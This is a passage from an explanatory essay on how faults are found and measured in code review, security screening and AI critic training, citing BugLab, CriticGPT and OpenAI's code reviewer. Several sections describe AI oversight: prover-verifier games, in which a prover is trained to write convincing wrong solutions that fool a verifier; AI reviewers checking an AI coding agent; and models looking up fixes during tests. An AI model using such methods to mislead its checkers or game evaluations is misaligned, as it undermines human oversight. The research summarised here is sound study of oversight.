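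Two runs of one model are even less independent. *PROBE* (Paina, Müller et al., 2026) had AI models search whole projects for bugs. Within a given type of bug, runs of GPT-5.6 Luna typically overlapped 6.3 times as much with one another as with the bugs the projects' developers had fixed. If two runs find exactly the same bugs, the formula implies that none are left.

Software engineers have long known about this bias. Ahrefors, Thelin and colleagues (2004), in *Capture-recapture in software inspections after 10 years research*, date the method's first use in software inspection to 1992. Wohlin, Runeson and Brantestam, in *An Experimental Evaluation of Capture-Recapture in Software Inspections*, also found that the method underestimates the remaining faults, and proposed a correction based on past experience. None of the models tested in *Quantitative evaluation of capture-recapture models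 to control software inspections* was accurate enough with fewer than four inspectors.

False alarms, by contrast, make the estimate too high. If the first reviewer has found every real fault and only half of the second reviewer's reports are right, the formula gives twice the true total. Someone therefore has to check the reports before counting them.

The method doesn't work for a single text with one decisive token. If both reviewers miss it, n1, n2 and m are all zero. The simple formula is then undefined, and Chapman's version estimates zero faults.

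### Where the test items come from

Planted faults can be easier to find than natural ones, as they were in the test on chip designs. Organisers can reduce this problem by copying faults from past incidents and asking someone who did not design the reviewer to choose them. This is harder for sabotage, because there are few known cases and the most successful ones may still be undiscovered.

Real bugs cause a different problem, because researchers usually know only about the ones someone fixed. Paina and colleagues collected 2,457 bugs that the developers of 20 projects had fixed over 18 months, and asked ten models to search the code from the start of that period. No model found more than 21% of the bugs, and at most 8.1% of a model's reports matched one of them. But when other models checked a sample of the reports, they judged about 85% valid. The researchers graded some of these reports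 themselves and usually agreed with the models' judgments.

So most of the apparent false alarms were real bugs that nobody had fixed yet. Paina and colleagues estimate that developers would fix between 5,200 and 9,400 of the original bugs within five to ten years. A reviewer that reported all the original bugs and nothing else would have a measured precision of only 26–47%.

Wrong calculations and comparisons also made up only 10% of the developers' list of fixed bugs, compared with 19% of the models' reports. A test built from such a list may therefore give too little weight to faults that a single operator can cause. Sashiko's 53% hit rate on kernel bugs comes from a list of this kind.

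In *CR-Bench*, Pereira, Sinha and colleagues (2026) found a similar gap between matching a known bug and making a useful comment. Only 3–5% of the comments from four AI reviewers identified the known bug, but another model judged 48–84% of all their comments useful. When the researchers had GPT-5.2 search again for anything it had missed, its hit rate rose from 27% to 33%, but the share of useful comments fell from 84% to 66%.

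When a test uses publicly known bugs, the answers can also leak to the model. CAISI, the US government's centre for testing AI, found that some models working on known bugs in public software had looked up a later version of the program, which contained the fix. A model may also have seen the answer in training. OpenZeppelin (2026), a company that checks blockchain programs for flaws, raised this concern about EVMBench, a test based on 120 known vulnerabilities. A model that has memorised a public report can name the flaw without being able to find a new one.

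Yang and colleagues deleted each project's later history and restricted internet access. They also tested models on 800 changes from a company's private code, where scores fell by up to 25.5 percentage points. Leaked answers might explain part of the gap, but the private bugs were also harder. Only 23% were visible in the diff itself, against 46% of the public bugs.

AWS publishes its samples without the labels and includes 5,127 that aren't scored, so companies can't easily tune a product to the answers. The company running a test still has a great deal of influence if it also sells a product. In *Snyk VulnBench JS 1.0* (2026), Snyk, a security company, scored 100% in every category with its own scanner because the scanner's findings were the answer key. Claude Opus 4.6 scored 0% in several categories, which means only that it reported none of the scanner's findings in them. Finding a real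 flaw that the scanner had missed could not raise the model's score, because the flaw wasn't in the key.

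## Training people and models to find them

Planted faults can both measure and improve a reviewer's performance. Airports add images of fake bombs and guns to the bag scans their staff inspect, and AI companies train models on deliberately broken programs. Telling reviewers what to look for takes much less effort than planting faults.

### Asking for security problems

In the holiday experiment, the warning about a security weakness came after a first review, so reading the code a second time may also have helped reviewers. Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues (2022) avoided this problem in *Less is More* by randomly assigning 150 people, most of them software engineers, to four groups with different instructions. Everyone reviewed the same 160 lines of Java, which registered new users of a website.

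The code had two weaknesses. When a database command failed, the program copied users' private details into a log file. The other was a single word, "MD5", the name of an outdated method of scrambling passwords that attackers can break quickly.

| Instructions | Reviewers | Found the log fault | Found "MD5" |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing about security | 33 | 3% | 21% |
| Look for security problems | 41 | 46% | 61% |
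| The same, plus a 22-item checklist | 35 | 46% | 57% |
| The same, plus a 7-item checklist written for this change | 41 | 46% | 68% |

Without the instruction, 8 of the 33 reviewers in the study by Braz and colleagues found at least one weakness (24%), compared with 84 of 117 in the other groups (72%). The share tripled, which is a very large effect for one sentence of advice. Braz and colleagues say the instruction made reviewers eight times more likely to find a weakness, but that figure is a ratio of odds.

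The checklists had no statistically significant effect. The difference between 61% and 68% has a margin of error of about 21 percentage points, so the short checklist may have helped a little or not at all. The short checklist was close to ideal, because the researchers knew which weaknesses the code contained and kept only the relevant items.

Some reviewers lacked knowledge that neither an instruction nor a checklist provided. One reviewer with a checklist considered MD5 and decided it was a good choice. Others said the checklist made them go back and notice the algorithm, or look up how strong it was.

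Each person in the experiment did only one review, and all the code was faulty, so it can't show whether the instruction would still work after a hundred reviews or how many false alarms it would cause on clean code. Telling reviewers to look for security problems would also be a poor way to help them find other errors, such as a wrong discount.

After the Pvote review, computer scientist Dan Sandler proposed a "read-write review", in which reviewers edit the code while they study it. This might help because rewriting a condition requires working out what it does, while someone only reading could skim past it. This is a conjecture, and reviewers would have to discard their edits afterwards or check them as carefully as the original.

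### False bombs in real luggage

Threat Image Projection inserts a stored X-ray image of a bomb, gun or knife into the image of a real passenger's bag. Screeners get a message when they find a projected item, miss one, or raise an alarm when the system projected nothing (Hofer and Schwaninger, 2005, *Using Threat Image Projection Data for Assessing Individual Screener Performance*).

Buser, Schwaninger and colleagues report in *Reliability and validity of threat image projection data* that airports add fake threats to the images of 1–4% of bags. After finding a fake item, the screener has to inspect the bag's image again without it, in case a fake gun distracted them from a real knife.

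The system is meant to keep screeners alert by making targets less rare, which should reduce the prevalence effect. It also records each person's hit rate. The European Union requires extra training for screeners who score too low.

The evidence for the second purpose is good. Buser and colleagues analysed about 1.2 million projected items shown to 728 screeners at one European airport over four years, along with nearly 1,200 covert tests in which people tried to carry real prohibited items through security. Screeners who scored better on the projected items were more likely to catch the real ones. An earlier study by other researchers had found such a link in one dataset but not in another.

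A score needs many items to be meaningful, because some items are much harder to see than others. *Reliability* is the share of the variation in scores that comes from real differences between people and not from luck. About 100 items per screener gave a reliability of 0.7, as long as the items weren't too easy. If r is the reliability of a test, a test k times as long has a reliability of:

new reliability = kr ÷ (1 + (k − 1)r)

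Reaching 0.9, which experts recommend when a score affects somebody's job, would therefore take about 390 items.

None of this shows that the false items keep screeners alert. Testing that would require comparing screeners with and without the system on real items or covert tests. Laboratory results give only partial support, since bursts of common targets with feedback helped people but common targets mixed into the search did not.

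False items can also be recognizable as fake. In Riz à Porta, Sterchi and Schwaninger's *How Realistic Is Threat Image Projection for X-ray Baggage Screening?*, screeners rated 34% of the images as visibly artificial or as showing an unrealistic situation. For example, a bomb might seem to pass through the solid heel of a shoe or lie at an odd angle to everything else in the tray.

These flaws matter less than one might expect. In *Evaluating Artifact Effects in Threat Image Projection for X-Ray Baggage Screening*, Riz à Porta, Sterchi and Schwaninger (2025) showed 83 screeners images with and without them. Items at an odd angle were easier to find, but items that seemed to pass through other objects were not. The researchers estimate that removing the odd angles would raise the airport's miss rate from 11.7% to only 12.8%.

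Programmers have had a similar idea since the early 1970s, when Gerald Weinberg's book *The Psychology of Computer Programming* described "bebugging", or adding known bugs to a program to train, motivate and evaluate the people who look for them. But no well-known code review system works like the airport one, by secretly adding faults to everyday work and giving reviewers immediate feedback. Google shows its reviewers mutants, but it labels them as such and uses them to improve the tests.

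Code reviewers would see planted faults too slowly to be scored individually. If 2.9% of changes contained a planted fault, the rate at the airport in the study, a reviewer would have to read about 3,450 changes to see 100 faults. At ten changes a day, that would take 345 working days. A reviewer would also spend far more time on a planted fault than a screener spends on a false gun. A company could still use planted faults to give feedback or to measure a whole team, but it would struggle to rank individuals fairly.

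### How a model learns from seeded bugs

A model can review thousands of planted faults in the time a person needs for one. The training usually goes roughly as follows:

1. Someone takes a program that seems correct and changes a small part of it, such as `>=` to `>`.
2. They record where the change is and what the original said.
3. The model reads the changed program, without the record, and writes a critique.
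4. A person or another program compares the critique with the record, and the model gets a reward if it named the fault.
5. The training program adjusts the model's parameters so that critiques like the rewarded ones become more likely.

The record makes the fourth step much easier. Without it, someone would have to check whether each complaint was right, which can be as hard as the original review. Some of the programs should also stay unchanged, or the model will learn that every program has a fault.

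*Self-Supervised Bug Detection and Repair* (Allamanis, Jackson-Flux and Brockschmidt, 2021) describes BugLab, a system that trained two models together without needing people to plant the faults. One model chose a change to make, and the other had to find and undo it or report that nothing was wrong. The first learned to choose changes that were difficult for the second, so the exercises became harder as training went on.

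Nearly all the changes were of the smallest kind that can flip correctness: a wrong operator, variable, number or true/false value, or two swapped arguments. Even one short function had 63 possible changes. Finding the fault was harder than repairing it, because a function has many places to look but only a few plausible alternatives at each.

BugLab's output was a location and a replacement. A language model can also explain what is wrong, which helps a person decide whether to believe it.

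### CriticGPT and its invented bugs

OpenAI trained a model called CriticGPT to write such explanations. For *LLM Critics Help Catch LLM Bugs* (McAleese, Pokorny and colleagues, 2024), contractors inserted subtle bugs into code that ChatGPT had written and described each bug as if they had caught it in a review. They were also supposed to confirm that an existing AI critic missed the bug in at least one of three attempts.

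The contractors then compared several critiques of the same code. As in OpenAI's experiments with the reversed reward, a second model learned to predict people's ratings, and CriticGPT learned to write critiques that this model rated highly. Knowing about the bug helped people judge the critiques more consistently.

CriticGPT caught many more of the planted bugs than contractors who reviewed the code themselves. The contractors typically had five years' experience with Python and spent about 50 minutes on each example. McAleese and colleagues think the main reason for the gap was that people wrote shorter reviews. Some also didn't know the Python libraries involved. The researchers expect some people could have beaten the model, so the result applies to OpenAI's usual contractors rather than the best human reviewers.

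Some contractors started from CriticGPT's critique and could delete, edit or add comments. On bugs that ChatGPT had made by itself, the three kinds of review compared as follows:

| Reviewer | Covers the serious problems | Invented bugs and trivial complaints | Preferred to a person's review |
|---|---|---|---|
| Person alone | Least | Fewest | – |
| CriticGPT alone | More | Most | 63% |
| Person with CriticGPT | About as much as CriticGPT | In between | 60% |

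The people contributed mainly by removing bad comments. They added few comments of their own, much like the experts in the study by Tufano and colleagues, who tended to look where the model had commented.

CriticGPT often made good and bad comments together. For example, one program was supposed to open only files in the folder `/safedir`, so it checked whether each file's path began with those characters. CriticGPT correctly objected that files in a similarly named folder, such as `/safedir2`, would also pass. It then complained that the program opened files only for reading, although nobody had asked it to do anything else with them.

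CriticGPT could trade hits against false alarms without new training. It wrote 28 candidate critiques, and a program chose the one with the highest value of:

predicted rating + bonus × number of passages criticised

A larger bonus favours longer critiques, which report more real bugs and more invented ones. The researchers did not know which setting would be best for producing training data. Training reduced the number of invented bugs, but they still described the rate as quite high.

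### Fewer false alarms or more hits

*A Practical Approach to Verifying Code at Scale* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2025) describes the code reviewer that OpenAI trained as part of its GPT-5-Codex and GPT-5.1-Codex-Max models. OpenAI deliberately accepted a lower hit rate in exchange for fewer false alarms, because programmers stop using a reviewer that wastes their time.

Trębacz and colleagues want the reviewer to make comments with a high expected value. If p is the probability that a comment is right:

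value = p × cost saved − cost of checking − (1 − p) × cost of a false alarm

Suppose checking a comment takes 5 minutes and a false alarm distracts the reader for another 10. If the bug would waste an hour, the comment is worth making when the chance that it is right is above 21%. That threshold rises to 75% for a bug that would waste only 10 minutes and falls to 0.25% for one that would waste 100 hours.

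By this rule, a reviewer should report a possible backdoor even if there probably isn't one. But the rule works only if the reviewer judges the stakes correctly. A single wrong operator can look trivial, so a reviewer that stays quiet about small problems may withhold the comment that was needed.

OpenAI uses separate checkers for training and for daily work. The checker used to train a code-writing model should catch as many mistakes as possible, and false alarms do less harm there. It may also have extra information about the task. The checker that people use has to infer what the programmer wanted, often from incomplete descriptions. If one checker did both jobs, the code-writing model might learn to pass its checks by writing overcautious code, which would make the checker less useful to people.

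CriticGPT saw short pieces of code, but the newer reviewer can search the whole project and run programs. In OpenAI's tests, this access helped GPT-5 catch more critical problems and raise fewer false alarms, and training for code review improved the results further.

By October 2025 the reviewer was handling more than 100,000 outside pull requests a day. Within OpenAI, it commented on 36% of the pull requests that the company's coding agent wrote alone, and 46% of those comments led to a code change. On pull requests written by people, 53% of its comments did.

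These figures are a rough guide to whether comments are useful. An author may change the code just to satisfy the reviewer, or ignore a correct comment about something unimportant. The figures also don't measure missed bugs. OpenAI reports that fewer accepted changes needed a later bug fix, which is encouraging, but it gives no figure, and other things may also have changed.

The reviewer and the coding agent are the same underlying model with different tasks, so they might share blind spots. OpenAI watches for this by comparing how well the reviewer does on code written by people and code written by the agent. So far, OpenAI considers the reviewer similarly effective on both. However, when the researchers limited the reviewer's reasoning, its ability to find known bugs fell more on the agent's code than on people's.

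### Learning from solutions meant to mislead

BugLab made its exercises harder by choosing difficult changes. *Prover-verifier training* goes further, because one model writes entire wrong solutions that are meant to convince another. Kirchner, Chen and colleagues (2024), in *Prover-Verifier Games improve legibility of LLM outputs*, tried it on grade-school maths problems with known answers. In outline, each round has two stages:

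1. A small model, the *verifier*, learns to tell correct solutions from wrong ones.
2. A larger model, the *prover*, learns to play two roles. In the helpful role it tries to write correct solutions that the verifier accepts, and in the "sneaky" role it tries to write wrong ones that the verifier accepts.

In the next round, the researchers train a new verifier on data that includes the misleading solutions from earlier rounds. They know the answer to every problem, so they can label the wrong solutions correctly, however convincing they looked.

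Verifiers from later rounds were harder to fool. Kirchner and colleagues tested this by training separate provers solely to mislead the verifiers, and these provers generally needed more training to succeed as the rounds went on. Larger verifiers were also harder to fool. Against verifiers a hundredth of the prover's size, none of the three attacks succeeded after the first round within the 8,000 training steps allowed. Verifiers a thousandth of the prover's size remained vulnerable to two of the attacks for several more rounds. The researchers stress that these attacks are far from a complete test.

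The wrong solutions also changed, from early ones with several obvious mistakes to later ones that were mostly sound, with the error in one small place, such as an equation that did not match the words of the problem. Reviewers of isolated errors need examples like the later ones, and the researchers suggest using such a prover to create exercises for critics like CriticGPT.

People who had 45 seconds per solution also found the later wrong solutions harder to spot, but the researchers warn that this test had design flaws. They have better evidence that the helpful role's correct solutions became easier for people to check as training went on. A model trained only to get the right answer solved more problems, but it eventually wrote solutions that people could hardly follow.

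The method needs a reliable source of right answers during training. Grade-school maths and programs with thorough tests have one, but contracts don't. If some contracts were wrongly labelled as correct, the verifier would learn to accept the errors in them.

### From seeded bugs to natural ones

The main objection to all this training is that planted bugs may differ from natural ones, so a model could become good at the exercise and remain poor at the job. BugLab's results support the objection strongly. Its best version located and repaired 70.3% of faults planted at random, but only 26.4% of 2,374 real bugs that developers had fixed in Python projects. The table shows how often it located some of the main types:

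| Fault | Planted at random | Real |
|---|---|---|
| Wrong assignment operator, such as `=` for `+=` | 96.1% | 20.0% |
| Wrong comparison operator | 83.9% | 33.7% |
| Wrong variable | 84.9% | 35.3% |
| Wrong number or true/false value | 71.7% | 21.6% |

The gap appears within each type, so training on the wrong types can't fully explain it. The real bugs had probably survived some testing by their authors, who would have noticed obvious ones at once. Random changes haven't been filtered this way, and many produce code that no programmer would write.

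False alarms were an even larger problem. Allamanis and colleagues checked 1,000 of BugLab's warnings on popular Python packages, and only 19 were real bugs. Part of the reason was that some of the planted "bugs" were equivalent mutants, changes that don't affect what the program does, and BugLab had learned to flag them. For example, Python's `find` never returns a number below −1, so `x.find(y) <= -1` and `x.find(y) == -1` always give the same result.

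Harder exercises narrowed the gap a little. When the model that planted the bugs learned to choose difficult ones instead of random ones, the score on random bugs barely changed, from 69.4% to 69.6%, but the score on real bugs rose from 21.2% to 24.2%. A test that used only planted bugs would have missed most of this benefit.

The results for CriticGPT are more favourable. People preferred its critiques to human ones more than 80% of the time on planted bugs and 63% of the time on natural ones. Part of that drop may have come from better human critiques, because people found the natural bugs more easily. McAleese and colleagues also trained a version without planted bugs, which did much worse on both kinds in automatic tests. So training on planted bugs helped the model with natural ones too, probably because it made the ratings the model learned from more consistent.

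But CriticGPT also learned to leave out types of error that were rare among the planted bugs. Without the search over 28 critiques, it could cover fewer of the serious natural problems than ordinary ChatGPT did. ChatGPT had received more training, though, and CriticGPT did better than a version of ChatGPT trained a similar amount.

People had already caught all the natural bugs in this test, so these bugs are a poor substitute for the ones that matter most. Two other experiments went beyond them. In the first, CriticGPT looked for problems in ChatGPT training data that a contractor had rated "flawless", most of which was not code. When it reported a problem, a second contractor agreed in 24% of cases that the answer deserved a substantially lower rating. Without a critique, second contractors gave similarly low ratings to only 6% of "flawless" answers. The critiques may have swayed some contractors,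 but the fourfold difference suggests that the model found real problems outside the area it was trained on.

In the second experiment, an early critic's comments did not significantly help contractors tell which of two solutions to a hard programming problem passed its tests. The contractors had 20 minutes and could not run either solution. The researchers had needed many attempts to get a correct solution, and the critic could not spot the faults in the wrong ones.

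These critics are now old, and the gap between planted and natural faults looks much smaller for current models. In Mahmud's test on chip designs, models missed about three times as many real mistakes as planted operators, but they still caught nearly all of both. This is only a rough comparison with BugLab, because Mahmud's models could read a specification and had not trained on that exercise. Even in 2026, specialised training on planted flaws can fall short, as it did for the Japanese contract model.
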